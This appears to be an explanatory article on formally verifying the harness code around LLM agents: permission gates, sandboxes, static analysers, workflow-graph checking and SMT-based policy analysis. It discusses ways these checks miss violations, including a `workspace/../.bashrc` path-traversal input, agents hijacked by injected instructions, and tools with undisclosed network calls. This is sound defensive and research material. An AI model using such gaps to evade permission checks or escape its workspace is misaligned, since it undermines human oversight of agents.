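# Formal verification of the software around LLM agents: soundness and false alarms

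## The code around a language model and what it means to check it

A language model takes text as input and returns text. It cannot open a file or send an email by itself. An LLM agent is a language model joined to an ordinary computer program that does these things. The program sends text to the model, carries out the actions specified in the reply, and feeds the results back until the task ends. Engineers call this program the harness. *The Last Harness You'll Ever Build* (2026) defines it as all code, configuration and execution logic that is not the model.

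Formal verification means showing, by exhaustive search or mathematical proof, that a program obeys an exactly stated rule. The harness suits this treatment because it is conventional code. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) describes the component that carries out the model's requests as "a regular, deterministic program". The model's output, by contrast, varies from run to run, and nobody can list in advance the texts it might produce.

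A check that misses nothing usually also flags some harmless behaviour, and these false alarms take up developers' time, interrupt users and stop agents from finishing legitimate work.

### The parts of a harness

Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues (2026), in *Harness Engineering*, read the source code of eleven agents, most of them built for programming, including Claude Code (from the AI company Anthropic), Codex (OpenAI) and Gemini CLI (Google). They divide every harness into seven parts:

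- the agent loop, which alternates between calling the model and acting on its reply;
- the connection to the model, which also assembles the prompt;
- the tools, which define what the agent can do;
- memory and context, which ration the text that the model sees;
- safety and permissions;
- orchestration, which starts and coordinates further agents;
- extensibility, through which users add capabilities.

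The smallest of the eleven, Mini-SWE-Agent, covers the list in roughly 100 lines of core code, partly because it omits orchestration. Codex has about 1.1 million lines. None of the eleven imports a general-purpose agent framework such as LangChain to run its loop, so an analyser that looks for such a framework's function names would find nothing in them.

### One tool call from start to finish

The running example, from Adam and colleagues, is a small tool called `write_file`. It takes a path and some content, opens the file at that path and writes the content into it. The tool may write only inside the workspace folder, which holds the user's project. It may therefore write to `workspace/test/tests.py`, but writing to `$HOME/.bashrc`, a file of commands that a Unix shell runs when it starts, breaks the rule.

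Suppose a user asks the agent to add a test. The harness sends the model the conversation along with a description of each tool and its arguments. The model replies with a tool call, a block of structured text that holds an identifier, the name `write_file` and the two arguments. Nothing on the disk has changed yet, because the model "never runs anything on its own" (Anthropic, *How tool use works*).

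The harness, which is ordinary code, then parses the block and extracts the name, identifier and arguments. If the path is missing, the harness can return an error message, and the model will usually retry with the path included, according to Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*. When a reply is cut off at the length limit, its arguments can be incomplete and still pass validation, since a truncated path is often a valid path. Pi, one of the agents that Barbaste and colleagues studied, therefore rejects every tool call in a reply that was cut off.

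The call next reaches the permission gate, the code that allows it, denies it or refers it to a person. Anthropic's documentation describes six steps for Claude Code. The gate runs hooks, which are scripts the user supplies, then checks deny rules, ask rules, the session's permission mode and allow rules. If the call is still undecided, it goes to a function written by the application's developer, which typically shows an approval prompt. Docker's agent software checks deny rules, then allow rules, then ask rules. The difference matters when a configuration allows file writes in general but asks for confirmation in one important folder. A write to that folder brings up a prompt in Claude Code but goes through without one under Docker's order. Anyone who verifies a gate therefore has to reproduce its exact order.

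Some gates use a model as well as ordinary code. In Claude Code's auto mode, a second model decides whether to allow actions such as shell commands. Codex has a similar reviewer and denies the action if the reviewing model times out or returns malformed output. A proof can cover that fallback but not the reviewer's verdict.

If the gate allows the call, the harness looks up the tool by name and runs it. The tool is also ordinary code, but often someone else wrote it. Agents commonly get tools through the Model Context Protocol, an open standard for connecting them to outside tool servers, and the description the model reads may not match what the tool does. The version of `write_file` that Adam and colleagues show also sends the size of the content to a metrics service, which its description doesn't mention. For a few tools, such as web search, Anthropic runs the code on its own servers,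 and the application's developer has no source code to check.

Finally, the harness labels the output with the call's identifier, adds it to the conversation and calls the model again. This repeats as long as the model's replies contain tool calls. *Agents' Last Exam* (2026) finds broadly the same loop in Claude Code, Codex and OpenClaw.

Instructions in the prompt are not part of this code, even when they are worded as if they were. Anthropic tells Claude Code's users that the program enforces permission rules, while instructions to the model only shape what the model tries to do. OpenCode, another of the eleven agents, describes its editing tool to the model as returning an error if the model has not read the file first. Barbaste and colleagues looked for code that does this and found none.

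### From a rule in English to a specification

The instruction "Write only inside the workspace folder" is too vague for a checker, even though a person would understand it. The path `workspace/../.bashrc` starts with the right folder name but leads outside the folder. The instruction also doesn't specify whether it covers only `write_file` or every way of changing a file. In Claude Code, a rule that denies edits to a folder blocks the agent's file tools and shell commands that redirect output there. Anthropic warns that a script the agent runs can still write to the folder if the script opens files itself. A rule can also fail because of its wording. Claude Code applies path rules for all file-writing tools under the name `Edit`, so a path rule written under `Write` never matches a call.

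A specification settles such questions in an exact notation. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, treat an agent's plan as a finite sequence of actions, π = (a₁, …, aₙ), and a safety rule as a formula φ in temporal logic, a notation for statements about what happens over time. Verification asks whether π ⊨ φ, that is, whether the plan satisfies the formula. For the running example one could write

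φ = G ( write(p) → inside(resolve(p), W) )

Here G means "at every step", p is a path, W is the workspace folder, and resolve turns a path into the location it really leads to. The formula means that whenever the agent writes to a path, the location it leads to is inside the workspace.

No checker can tell whether φ is the rule the user wanted, so even a flawless proof of a mistranslated rule doesn't show that the software follows the intended one. Language models did poorly at this kind of translation on one benchmark that Dantas and colleagues cite, where only 24.8% to 34.2% of their translations from English into a formal planning language kept the original meaning.

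### Four ways to check

Static analysis examines a program's source code without running it. Given a rule or a list of operations to look for, it reports the places where the program may break the rule. Adam and colleagues built an analyser for tools written in the Rust programming language that returns a summary of each tool's effects. For `write_file`, the summary shows that the content can reach both the file system and the network, which reveals the hidden metrics line. The summary is less useful for checking the workspace rule. The path is known only when the tool runs, so the analyser must allow for every possible path, and it reports a possible violation even if every real call stays inside the folder. The next section explains why a sound analysis over-reports in this way.

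A model checker takes a formula such as φ and a finite description of a system's states and the transitions between them. This description is also called a model, but it is unrelated to language models. The checker explores every reachable state and either confirms that the formula holds or returns a counterexample, a step-by-step run that violates it. For a permission gate, the states might be "requested", "awaiting approval", "approved" and "executed", and a counterexample might show two simultaneous writes using the same approval.

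Theorem proving can cover infinitely many cases, such as every path that anyone could type. A person or an automated tool writes a proof of a statement about a program, or about a model of the program, and a proof checker accepts or rejects it. Two recent harness projects do this in Lean, a language for writing programs and machine-checked proofs about them. In *Agenra* (2026), Python code passes each tool call to Lean functions, which compare it with the state of the task and use up any quota or approval before the tool runs. *L3M* (2026) lets an agent write new tools for itself in Lean, and the harness offers a new tool to the model only if the agent's existing permissions cover it.

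The two methods can also be combined. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) verifies a small gate that decides whether an agent's action may take effect. Two of the gate's four rules are that a rejected action never takes effect and that an action which needs approval waits for it. The work starts with a proof for one decision at a time, then exhaustively searches finite cases with concurrent requests, then gives a proof without that bound. A last check runs the deployed code through a limited number of thread orderings, and it found two real defects that testing had missed. The paper acknowledges that the first three stages concern the same abstract model, so they are not separate verifications of the program, and that the link between model and code depends on tests.

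Run-time enforcement takes a policy and a concrete action that is about to happen, and returns a decision to allow, deny or ask. Examples are the permission gate and the sandbox, which limits what running code can read, write or contact. Because the sandbox acts just before a write, the path is already known, so it can allow `workspace/test/tests.py` and block `.bashrc`. Each decision covers only one call, so checking that the gate handles every call correctly requires applying one of the other three methods to the gate's own code.

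### Counting the mistakes

In a hypothetical run of 1,000 `write_file` calls, 50 target locations outside the workspace, and a gate must classify each call using incomplete information.

| | Gate blocks the call | Gate lets the call run | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call breaks the rule | 45 | 5 | 50 |
| Call obeys the rule | 95 | 855 | 950 |
| Total | 140 | 860 | 1,000 |

The 95 blocked calls that obey the rule are false alarms, and the 5 calls that break the rule but still run are missed violations. Precision is the share of blocked calls that break the rule, 45 of 140, or about 32%. Recall is the share of rule-breaking calls that the gate blocks, 45 of 50, or 90%. The false-positive rate is the share of rule-obeying calls that the gate blocks, 95 of 950, or 10%.

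Precision depends on how common violations are. If only 10 of the 1,000 calls broke the rule, a gate with the same recall and the same 10% false-positive rate would block 9 violations and 99 harmless calls, and its precision would drop to about 8%. Agents on everyday tasks are probably closer to this case, since most of their writes are harmless.

Soundness and completeness are claims about all possible runs. A check is sound if, given its stated assumptions, it never misses a violation of its rule, so the cell that holds 5 would be zero in every run. A check is complete if it never raises a false alarm, so the cell that holds 95 would always be zero. Missing no violations in a test gives 100% recall on that test but does not establish soundness. Either property is easy to get alone, since a gate that blocks everything is sound and one that allows everything is complete. Dantas and colleagues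 reviewed 38 studies and found no approach that combined soundness and completeness with scalability, faithful specifications and preserved usefulness. They favour the safe success rate, the share of tasks that the agent completes correctly without breaking the rule, because useless gates cannot score well on it. A gate that blocks everything would score close to zero.

### Three forms of a false alarm

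A static analyser's false alarm is a mistaken report to a developer, such as "`write_file` may write outside the workspace" for a tool that only ever receives safe paths. The program keeps working, but someone spends time reading and dismissing the report. Each report refers to a place in the code, and it is hard to say how many harmless places a program contains, so precision is a more natural measure than the false-positive rate. Precision cannot be converted into the false-positive rate of a gate that judges calls.

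At run time, a false alarm can be a needless block. The harness refuses a harmless write, and the model receives an error and may find another route or abandon the task. Whether a block is needless depends on the rule used to judge it. In one test by Adam and colleagues, a developer explicitly wanted instructions added to `.bashrc`, and a sandbox with a fixed policy refused the write. The block was correct under the sandbox's policy but a false alarm given what the user had asked for. Studies that report a false-positive rate have to choose one of these standards, and the choice can change the rate a lot.

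The third form is a needless approval prompt. The gate cannot determine that a call is harmless, so it asks a person. Claude Code asks for approval of any shell command longer than 10,000 characters, because Anthropic's parser does not handle them. It also asks about certain commands that change folder and then run the version-control program git, even when each half only reads files. One prompt takes a few seconds, but many wear down the user's attention, which a later section discusses.

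When nobody is there to answer a permission prompt, the gate blocks the action instead. Claude Code has a mode that denies every action it would otherwise prompt for, and OpenCode rejects all such requests when it runs unattended. A gate with the same rules can therefore produce mostly prompts on a developer's laptop and mostly blocks on an unattended server.

### What such checks do not cover

The workspace rule limits where an agent can write a file, but not what the file contains. An agent can write a test that checks nothing, or a comment that describes the code wrongly, and every method above will allow the write as long as the path is right. The rule doesn't limit what the model tells the user in its final message either. Some harnesses do turn part of the question of whether the agent's output is true into something code can check. Barbaste and colleagues describe an example in Hermes,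 an open-source agent. When the agent has changed code files and tries to finish without fresh evidence that it verified them, the harness sends it back to work. This guard establishes that the agent produced some evidence, but not that the code is correct.

The gate can't check intent either, for a similar reason. It has only the call and its recorded context, and a model hijacked by injected instructions can emit the same `write_file` call as a model that is helping its user. Adam and colleagues therefore treat the model and the tool server as untrusted and the user and the policy as trusted, and try to make the rule hold whatever the model does. Harm that the rule permits still gets through, such as malicious code that the agent writes inside the workspace and the user later runs.

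The proofs also don't cover the judgement of human reviewers. The Lean core of *Agenra* guarantees that an approval exists before an action that needs one, and that the action uses up the approval, but it can't guarantee that the reviewer was right to approve the action.

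## Why a sound analysis reports harmless behaviour

Better engineering can remove many false alarms like the one about `write_file`, but it cannot remove all of them without missing some violations, for mathematical reasons known decades before agents existed. Agents add another difficulty because the model's output determines which tools run and with which arguments, and that output cannot be predicted from the code.

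### Rice's theorem

In 1953 the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published a proof that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether the program's behaviour when it runs has a given property. The only exceptions are trivial properties, which all programs have or none do. For example, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it will ever write outside the workspace. The proof does not apply to properties of a program's text, such as its number of lines, which an algorithm can easily count.

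Rice's theorem concerns the results that programs compute, but the same argument works for file writes. Suppose Q is any program that writes no files, and a larger program runs Q and then writes to `.bashrc`. The larger program breaks the workspace rule exactly when Q finishes. A checker that was always right about the workspace rule could therefore determine whether any such Q finishes, but Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no algorithm can do this.

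By Rice's theorem, an automatic checker that always returns a verdict must be wrong about some programs. If the checker is sound, all its mistakes are false alarms. It must also raise false alarms on infinitely many programs, because a developer could list a finite number of them as exceptions and get the perfect checker that the theorem rules out.

The theorem does not establish how common these programs are. A sound analyser could in principle raise very few false alarms on the tools people write, so the number it raises in practice has to be measured. A person can still prove that a particular tool is safe. The theorem also does not apply to finite descriptions such as a workflow graph, where a search can visit every state.

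### Over-approximation

Patrick Cousot and Radhia Cousot set out abstract interpretation, the general theory of sound analysers, in 1977. The analyser steps through a program using descriptions of values, such as "any string", instead of the values themselves. At each step it computes a description that covers everything the real program could produce at that point. In a loop, it repeats this until the description stops growing.

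Let C be the set of all paths that a program could write to in any run, and let A be the description that the analyser ends up with. Write γ(A) for the set of all paths that fit the description. The analysis is sound if

C ⊆ γ(A)

that is, if the description covers every path the program can really use. Now let B be the set of forbidden paths, the ones outside the workspace. If γ(A) and B have no path in common, then C and B have none in common either, and the program is safe. If γ(A) and B do overlap, the analyser reports a possible violation. That report is a false alarm when the overlap contains only paths that are in γ(A) but not in C.

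Suppose a tool writes to `workspace/test/tests.py` or `workspace/notes.txt`, depending on a setting, and the analyser can describe a path only as "exactly this string" or "any string". It can describe the path in each branch exactly, but after the branches rejoin it needs one description that covers both paths, and only "any string" does. Because "any string" includes `.bashrc`, the analyser reports a harmless tool. A third kind of description, "starts with `workspace/` and contains no `..`", would cover both paths and remove the report, leaving aside file-system links that redirect one folder to another. But someone has to think of such a description, and each additional kind makes the analysis slower.

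This does not help with `write_file` itself, because its path is an argument and the tool does accept any string. Whether the report is a false alarm depends on who calls the tool.

### When the caller is a language model

In an ordinary program, other code calls `write_file`. If the analyser finds that every call passes a fixed path inside the workspace, it can drop the report. In an agent, the path comes from the model's reply, and a sound analyser must assume that reply could be any text.

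The same goes for the choice of tool. *AgentFlow* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a research agent that can search the web and hand its work to an operations agent, which can send email. The code does not determine which of these actions will happen, so the analyser includes every transfer the code permits. With five tools and ten calls there are 5¹⁰, or about 9.8 million, possible sequences, and a sound analysis has to cover all of them even if the model only ever uses a handful.

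Under this assumption, the result holds for every model, so it remains valid when the developer switches to a new model or when injected instructions take over the current one. However, the analysis cannot take prompts into account. If the prompt tells the agent to stay inside the workspace and the model always obeys, the analyser still has to report `write_file`. Only code can narrow the values the analyser has to consider. If the tool resolves the path and returns an error when the location is outside the workspace, the analyser can infer that any path that passes this check is inside, and it no longer reports the tool.

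The audit by Wang and colleagues only partly shows how many false alarms come from assuming that the model might do anything. Their analyser found possible routes from a prompt to a sensitive tool in 238 of 5,399 open-source agent projects. Two of the researchers then read the code behind 100 reports and judged 27 to be false. In 25 of those 27, the route existed but the analyser was wrong about what the tool could do. Thirteen cases involved local file access that neither wrote nor deleted anything, seven ran read-only database queries, and five were calculators that could not run general code. Most of the false alarms thus came from tool descriptions that were too coarse, which can be fixed. But the researchers did not run the agents, so they counted a route as a correct report even if no model would ever take it. The 73% precision is therefore weak evidence of how often the reported behaviour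 would occur.

### Agentproof

Some agents leave less to the model. In frameworks such as LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google's ADK, a developer can lay out the steps and the possible transitions between them in advance. Xavier, Jolly and colleagues (2026), in *Agentproof*, describe a tool that extracts a workflow graph from programs written in these four frameworks and checks it before the agent runs. (The eleven agents in the previous section run their own loops, so this method does not apply to them directly.)

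The graph is a tuple G = (V, E, κ_V, κ_E, T, v₀, V_f). V is a finite set of nodes, one for each step, and E is the set of directed edges between them. κ_V gives each node a kind: entry, exit, tool, LLM, router, human, subgraph or pass-through. κ_E marks each edge as direct, conditional, parallel or loop. T lists the tools that each tool node can call. v₀ is the single entry node, and V_f is the set of exit nodes.

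Agentproof runs six checks on this structure:

- every exit is reachable from the entry;
- every node reachable from the entry can itself reach some exit, which rules out cycles with no way out;
- every node other than an exit has an outgoing edge;
- every edge that leaves a router is conditional;
- the graph contains at least one human node;
- every tool node declares its tools.

Each check needs only a standard graph search or a pass over the nodes and edges. When a check fails because of a bad path, the tool prints that path. In one example, the developer of an email assistant added a drafting step for normal-priority messages but forgot to connect it to the sending step, so those messages silently stop there.

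A graph passes the human check even if its only human node is on a branch unrelated to any sensitive tool. An optional, stronger version requires every path from the entry to a sensitive tool to go through a human node. To check this, Agentproof deletes all human nodes and tests whether the sensitive tool is still reachable.

Rules about the order of events need more than this. Agentproof has a small language of seven forms for writing them, and it translates each rule into a finite automaton, which has a few states and a table that gives the next state for each state and event. One of the states means that the run has broken the rule.

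| Form | Meaning | States |
|---|---|---|
| `G !a` | a never happens | 2 |
| `a -> F b` | after a, b must happen before a happens again | 3 |
| `a U b` | a holds at every step until b happens | 3 |
| `a -> F[<=k] b` | after a, b must happen within k steps | k + 2 |
| `a -> F b -> F c` | after a, b and then c must happen before a happens again | n + 1 for a chain of n |
| `(A) AND (B)` | both rules hold | product of the two |
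| `(A) OR (B)` | at least one rule holds | product of the two |

The rule that an email draft needs a review, `tool:draft_email -> F tool:human_review`, compiles to an automaton with the states "idle", "waiting" and "violated". A draft moves the automaton from idle to waiting, a review moves it back, and a second draft while it is waiting moves it to violated. A run that drafts one email and ends without a review therefore stops in the waiting state and does not count as a violation. In standard temporal logic F means "eventually", so the compiled rule is weaker than the formula's standard meaning, and a developer who relies on that meaning could wrongly conclude that every drafted email gets a review.

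Agentproof checks a rule against the whole graph by searching over pairs (v, q), where v is a node and q is a state of the automaton. It begins with the entry node and the automaton's initial state. From each pair, it follows every edge out of the node and updates the automaton with the event that the next node produces. If it reaches a pair whose state is "violated", it reports the path that led there. There are at most |V| · |Q| pairs, where V is the set of nodes and Q is the set of automaton states, so the search always ends.

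The search reaches exactly the pairs that some path through the graph leads to, so it reports a violation if and only if some path breaks the compiled rule. Any mistake about the real program must come from the rule or the graph.

### A false alarm in five nodes

A small workflow based on the running example shows how a graph can produce a false alarm without containing a single wrong edge. The agent saves a new test in the workspace and, for some tasks, also has to change `.bashrc`. The rule is that a person must approve any change to `.bashrc` before it happens. The workflow has five nodes:

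- `start`, where ordinary code works out whether the task needs a change to `.bashrc` and stores the answer in a variable called `home`;
- `review`, where a person approves that change;
- `save`, which writes the test into the workspace;
- `write_home`, which changes `.bashrc`;
- `end`.

From `start`, the run goes to `review` if `home` is true and straight to `save` if it is false. `review` always leads to `save`. From `save`, the run goes to `write_home` if `home` is true and to `end` if it is false, and `write_home` leads to `end`. The value of `home` does not change during the run.

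The rule's automaton has the states "unreviewed", "reviewed" and "violated". The search begins at (`start`, unreviewed), which has edges to (`review`, reviewed) and (`save`, unreviewed). From (`save`, unreviewed), an edge leads to `write_home`. Nobody has reviewed anything on this path, so the next pair is (`write_home`, violated), and the search reports the path `start`, `save`, `write_home`. The stronger human check also reports it, because `write_home` is still reachable after `review` is deleted.

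No run can take this path. It needs `home` to be false at the first branch and true at the second. The graph has four paths from `start` to `end`, and the program can follow only two of them:

| Path | `home` at first branch | `home` at second branch | Can it happen? | Obeys the rule? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `start`, `save`, `end` | false | false | yes | yes |
| `start`, `review`, `save`, `write_home`, `end` | true | true | yes | yes |
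| `start`, `review`, `save`, `end` | true | false | no | yes |
| `start`, `save`, `write_home`, `end` | false | true | no | no |

Each of the six edges occurs in some real run. Xavier and colleagues call an extracted graph correct if it has exactly the program's steps and the transitions the program permits, and this graph meets that definition. The false alarm arises because the graph records which step can follow which, but not the value of `home` that led the run to a given step.

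Whether the alarm is false also depends on what decides the second branch. If the workflow prompted the model again after `save` to decide whether to change `.bashrc`, the first answer could be no and the second yes. The reported path would then be possible and the alarm correct, even though the graph would be the same.

Adding the value of `home` to each pair would remove the false alarm but could double the number of pairs to search. Ten independent variables of this kind could multiply the number by 1,024. Refinement methods, which a later section covers, add such details only where an alarm makes them necessary.

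### What the evaluation measured

Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows with 5 to 12 nodes each. They wrote the workflows themselves and deliberately included known mistakes. Five workflows had structural defects. Two had dead ends, one had an exit that no path reached, one had a router with the wrong kind of edge, and one had a tool node without declared tools. The structural checks found all the planted defects and raised no false alarms. Ten workflows had no human node. The researchers point out that these counts do not estimate how common such defects are in real projects, because they designed the set to contain defects.

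They also wrote 15 rules about the order of events and compared the exhaustive search with ten random simulated runs per workflow. The search found every violation of the forbidden-tool and follow-up rules that the random runs found, plus one they missed, an email draft without a human review. It never needed more than 24 pairs. The structural checks were also fast, taking about 105 milliseconds on an artificial graph with 5,000 nodes.

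The human check's reported precision of 0.75 is less informative than it seems, because it excludes findings that the researchers classed as "arguable" rather than true or false. One finding was false, so a precision of 0.75 implies three true ones, and the other six of the ten findings must have been arguable. Precision would be 30% if all six counted as false alarms and 90% if they all counted as correct.

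The one finding the researchers did count as false came from a rule that was too strict for the workflow, not from an impossible path. The workflow really had no human node, but its task carried so little risk that it arguably didn't need one. The researchers expect similar disputes about dead ends, since some developers use them on purpose to stop a run after an error.

Xavier and colleagues state that they did not measure false alarms like the one in the five-node example. They acknowledge that the search treats every conditional edge as possible and can therefore flag paths that no run would take. Their workflows would probably have shown few such cases anyway, because an average of 8.2 nodes and 8.2 edges leaves little room for one branch to depend on another. Larger workflows with more branches would be a harder test.

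### When the graph is wrong

The five-node graph had no wrong edges, but extracted graphs often will. Whether a wrong edge causes a false alarm or a missed violation depends on the kind of rule:

| Difference between graph and program | Rule that no path may do something | Rule that an exit must stay reachable |
|---|---|---|
| Extra edge | can cause a false alarm | can hide a defect |
| Impossible combination of correct edges | can cause a false alarm | can hide a defect |
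| Missing edge | can hide a violation | can cause a false alarm |

Over-approximation is therefore safe only for the first kind of rule. Suppose a loop ends when a counter passes five, but a bug resets the counter in each round. The graph has an edge from the loop to the exit, so Agentproof's exit checks pass even though the agent runs forever. *When Agents Do Not Stop* (2026) deals with loops that have no effective bound, and a later section covers its analyser. Xavier and colleagues say their search misses no rule violations, but this is true only if the graph has every edge that the program can take.

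Missing edges in the call graph, a map of which function can call which, are a particular problem in agent code because of how frameworks call tools. A developer typically writes a function, for example `write_file`, and puts a marker such as `@tool` on the line above it. The framework stores the function in a table under its name and looks it up there when the model requests the tool, so no line of the program calls `write_file` directly. An analyser that builds its call graph only from direct calls will treat the tool as code that never runs and report nothing about it.

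The obvious way to make the analysis sound is to assume that the lookup can return any function in the table. But if one agent may only read files, another may write them, and both use the same table, the analyser will report that the reading agent can write. Avoiding both missed behaviour and false alarms requires knowledge of each framework. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (2026) lists several ways that frameworks expose tools, including decorators (markers like `@tool`), registration calls, factories, workflow nodes and tool classes. Its analyser translates them into a common record that includes a confidence score for each match. Wang and colleagues modelled 143 such constructs across five frameworks. When they inspected 100 agents that had powerful tools but had not been reported, they still found 9 missed risks, mainly where developers had written their own wrappers or attached tools at run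 time.

General-purpose analysers do worse. *Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents* (Cai, Kim and Liu, 2026) tested three established tools on eight attacks against five open-source agent applications. It gave each tool the place where the malicious text entered and the place where it did harm, and tested whether the tool could connect the two. Joern and CodeQL failed on all eight attacks and Pysa on seven. In one case CodeQL did not connect the prompt to the language model's reply, because it had no model of the library that makes the call. The paper's own analyser found the entry point in all eight cases, but it cannot resolve framework lookups such as LangChain's either, and leaves those paths out of its graph.

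Other programs have this problem too. In *Agentic Root Cause Reasoning and Localization of Unsoundness in Static Call Graph*, Rafieian, Hicks and Wei (2026) compared the call graphs that three widely used Java analysers produce with the calls that happen when the programs run. Even with every available soundness option switched on, the three tools missed 1,459 calls in total. One cause, loading a class whose name is known only at run time, closely resembles tool lookup. When the researchers reported that one of the analysers, WALA, ignores certain calls that errors trigger, its maintainers answered that this was an intentional trade-off.

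Their study also gives reason to be cautious about testing extractors on small, hand-written programs. Only 2.9% of the calls missed in real-world programs matched a cause that the researchers had found in a set of such tests. Agentproof's extractors identified all nodes and edges correctly in 27 test cases, but those cases were simplified stand-ins for real workflows, and Xavier and colleagues note that the gap between them and real projects has not been measured. Their guarantee also no longer holds if a framework changes the graph while the agent is running, unless someone checks the new graph.

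Wrong labels on nodes cause similar errors. In LangGraph programs, Agentproof recognises a human node by looking for "human" in its name. It would treat a genuine approval step called `manager_signoff` as an ordinary model step and raise a false alarm. It would also accept a step called `humanize_text`, which only rewrites a draft, as a person's approval.

Missing a call can also cause false alarms, because the missed call may be the one that validates the input, as Rafieian and colleagues point out. If `write_file` checks its path through a function that the framework looks up by name, the analyser detects the write but misses the check, and reports a safe tool as unsafe.

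It is also hard to count such errors by running the program. Test runs can show that a call is missing from the graph, but they can't show that a path in the graph is impossible, because an untested run might take it. For this reason, Rafieian and colleagues decided not to report the precision of their warnings about where a call graph may be incomplete. To show that an analyser's alarm is false, one has to argue from the code that no run could take the path, as in the table of values for `home` in the five-node workflow.

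## Machine-checked proofs of permission rules

Most of the false alarms in the previous section arose because a checker analysing a whole program has to approximate values, branches and framework lookups. The rules inside a permission gate can be far simpler. A rule such as "allow refunds below $500" has no loops and calls no other code, so a tool can translate it into a logical formula with exactly the same meaning. A solver can then check that formula for every possible tool call at once, without false alarms about the rule itself. The rule can still block harmless calls if people wrote it too strictly.

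### A small rule with a gap

Suppose the gate for `write_file` allows a call if the path begins with `workspace/`. With p for the path, the rule is

allow(p) = startsWith(p, "workspace/")

In a path, `..` stands for the folder one level up, so an agent could use it to climb out of the workspace. The developer therefore writes down a requirement that no allowed path contains `..`:

for all p: allow(p) → ¬contains(p, "..")

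An SMT solver (short for satisfiability modulo theories) is a program that looks for values that make a formula true, where the formula can mix logic with numbers, text and other data. To check a claim about all paths, the tool negates the claim and gives the solver the result, which describes an exception:

startsWith(p, "workspace/") ∧ contains(p, "..")

The solver finds a value that fits, such as `workspace/..`, and returns it as a counterexample. From this the developer can see that `workspace/../.bashrc` would also get through, and adds a condition to the rule:

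allow(p) = startsWith(p, "workspace/") ∧ ¬contains(p, "..")

The description of an exception now becomes

startsWith(p, "workspace/") ∧ ¬contains(p, "..") ∧ contains(p, "..")

No text can both contain `..` and not contain it, so this formula has no solution. A solver that reports this has proved the requirement for paths of every length, which no finite set of tests can do. Solvers can always decide formulas like this one, because both conditions only compare the path with fixed text. With richer formulas, a solver may run out of time or fail to reach an answer, in which case it returns "unknown".

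### Cedar

Cedar is a language for writing permission rules, developed by AWS, Amazon's cloud computing company. AWS uses it in AgentCore Gateway, which sits between an agent and its remote tools and checks each tool call against a policy. AWS announced the policy feature as a preview in *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now includes Policy (preview), Evaluations (preview) and more* (2025) and has since released it.

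A Cedar policy is a set of `permit` and `forbid` statements. The language leaves out loops and operations that depend on stored state. Without loops, each statement unfolds into one formula of finite size, so the analysis has nothing to approximate. A call needs at least one matching `permit`, and any matching `forbid` overrides it. For a request r, the whole policy is therefore

allow(r) = (permit₁(r) ∨ … ∨ permitₘ(r)) ∧ ¬(forbid₁(r) ∨ … ∨ forbidₙ(r))

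The order of the statements makes no difference, unlike the order in which the gates of Claude Code and Docker check their rules.

AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives examples of mistakes that the analysis finds:

- A refund rule requires the customer's tier to be Gold and also Platinum. No customer has both, so the rule can never allow anything. Its author meant "or".
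- A discount rule applies to orders of at least 100 items, or of fewer than 100 items, or from Platinum customers. It allows every order.
- One statement permits refunds under $100 for Gold customers, and another forbids refunds under $500 for Gold and Platinum customers. Since `forbid` wins, Gold customers never get the refund.

Two of these three mistakes would have blocked legitimate requests, so the analysis can remove needless blocks as well as missed violations. It can also compare two versions of a policy. In AWS's example, a policy refuses bulk discounts on orders that include limited-edition products. An edit adds a condition, so that the policy refuses the discount only if the order also exceeds 200 items. The extra condition makes the policy less strict because it narrows the refusal, and an order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount. The analysis shows that the discount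 rule has become more permissive and that the refund rule is equivalent to the old one, but the company's staff must judge whether they wanted the change.

The same machinery also reduces blocked calls. When an agent requests the list of available tools, the gateway identifies those the policy would refuse whatever the arguments and leaves them out, so the model doesn't waste turns trying to call them.

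Cedar's exactness applies to the policy, not to the data in a request. In the discount example, the customer's tier comes from a login token that the model cannot alter, but the number of items and the product types come from the model's tool call. If the model leaves "limited edition" out of the list of product types, Cedar applies the policy correctly and allows the discount. To prevent this, the tool would have to look up the product types itself.

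Cedar keeps no state, so it gives identical requests the same decision every time. A rule that permits refunds below $500 therefore also permits ten refunds of $499 to the same customer, or $4,990 in total. A harness could keep a running total and add it to each request, but the analysis would then depend on ordinary code to keep that total correctly.

### Google's checker for CEL

The Common Expression Language (CEL) is a small language for writing conditions, such as rules about which workloads may start on Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) introduced a checker that translates CEL rules into formulas for Z3, an SMT solver. The company's main reason is that AI agents now write and edit these rules, and an agent can write a rule that passes the existing tests but handles other inputs incorrectly.

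In one of Google's examples, an edit was supposed to preserve a rule's meaning. The original rule allows ports 80 and 443 only in production. The edited rule is `is_prod && port == 80 || port == 443`. CEL applies "and" before "or", so the edited rule allows port 443 everywhere. The checker compares the two versions and returns a non-production request on port 443 as the counterexample.

In another example, an engineer assumes that every request uses either a port up to 80 or one above 1024, and the checker returns port 81 as a counterexample. A rule that admits only requests meeting this condition would also refuse port 443, the usual port for encrypted web traffic. It would therefore produce false alarms, while the gap in the edited rule would let unwanted requests through.

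Google claims that the checker has no false positives. Solvers can report false bugs when a rule calls a function they have no definition for, because they can assume any result for it. The checker tracks which findings depend on such functions and labels them "Inconclusive" instead of "Violated". Every reported violation should therefore be real, but someone still has to resolve the inconclusive findings by supplying a definition or reading the rule. The checker also limits how deeply it searches nested data, to keep computation manageable. Google's announcement does not specify which verdict a rule gets if its only flaw lies beyond that limit.

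### Rules that depend on earlier calls

Some rules, such as "send the report once", depend on what has already happened. *Agenra*, whose Lean core keeps track of quotas and approvals, shows how this dependence can make even a harmless-looking edit go wrong. Suppose permission 1 allows one deletion of object B, and permission 2 allows one deletion of object A. The gate searches the permissions in order and uses up the first one that fits, so an agent that deletes A and then B succeeds.

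A developer now widens permission 1 to cover either object. When the agent deletes A, the gate uses up permission 1. Only permission 2 is left, and it doesn't cover B, so the gate refuses a legitimate deletion of B that it used to allow. The agent can also now delete A twice, using one permission each time. Although the edit only added authority, it caused both a needless block and a missed violation.

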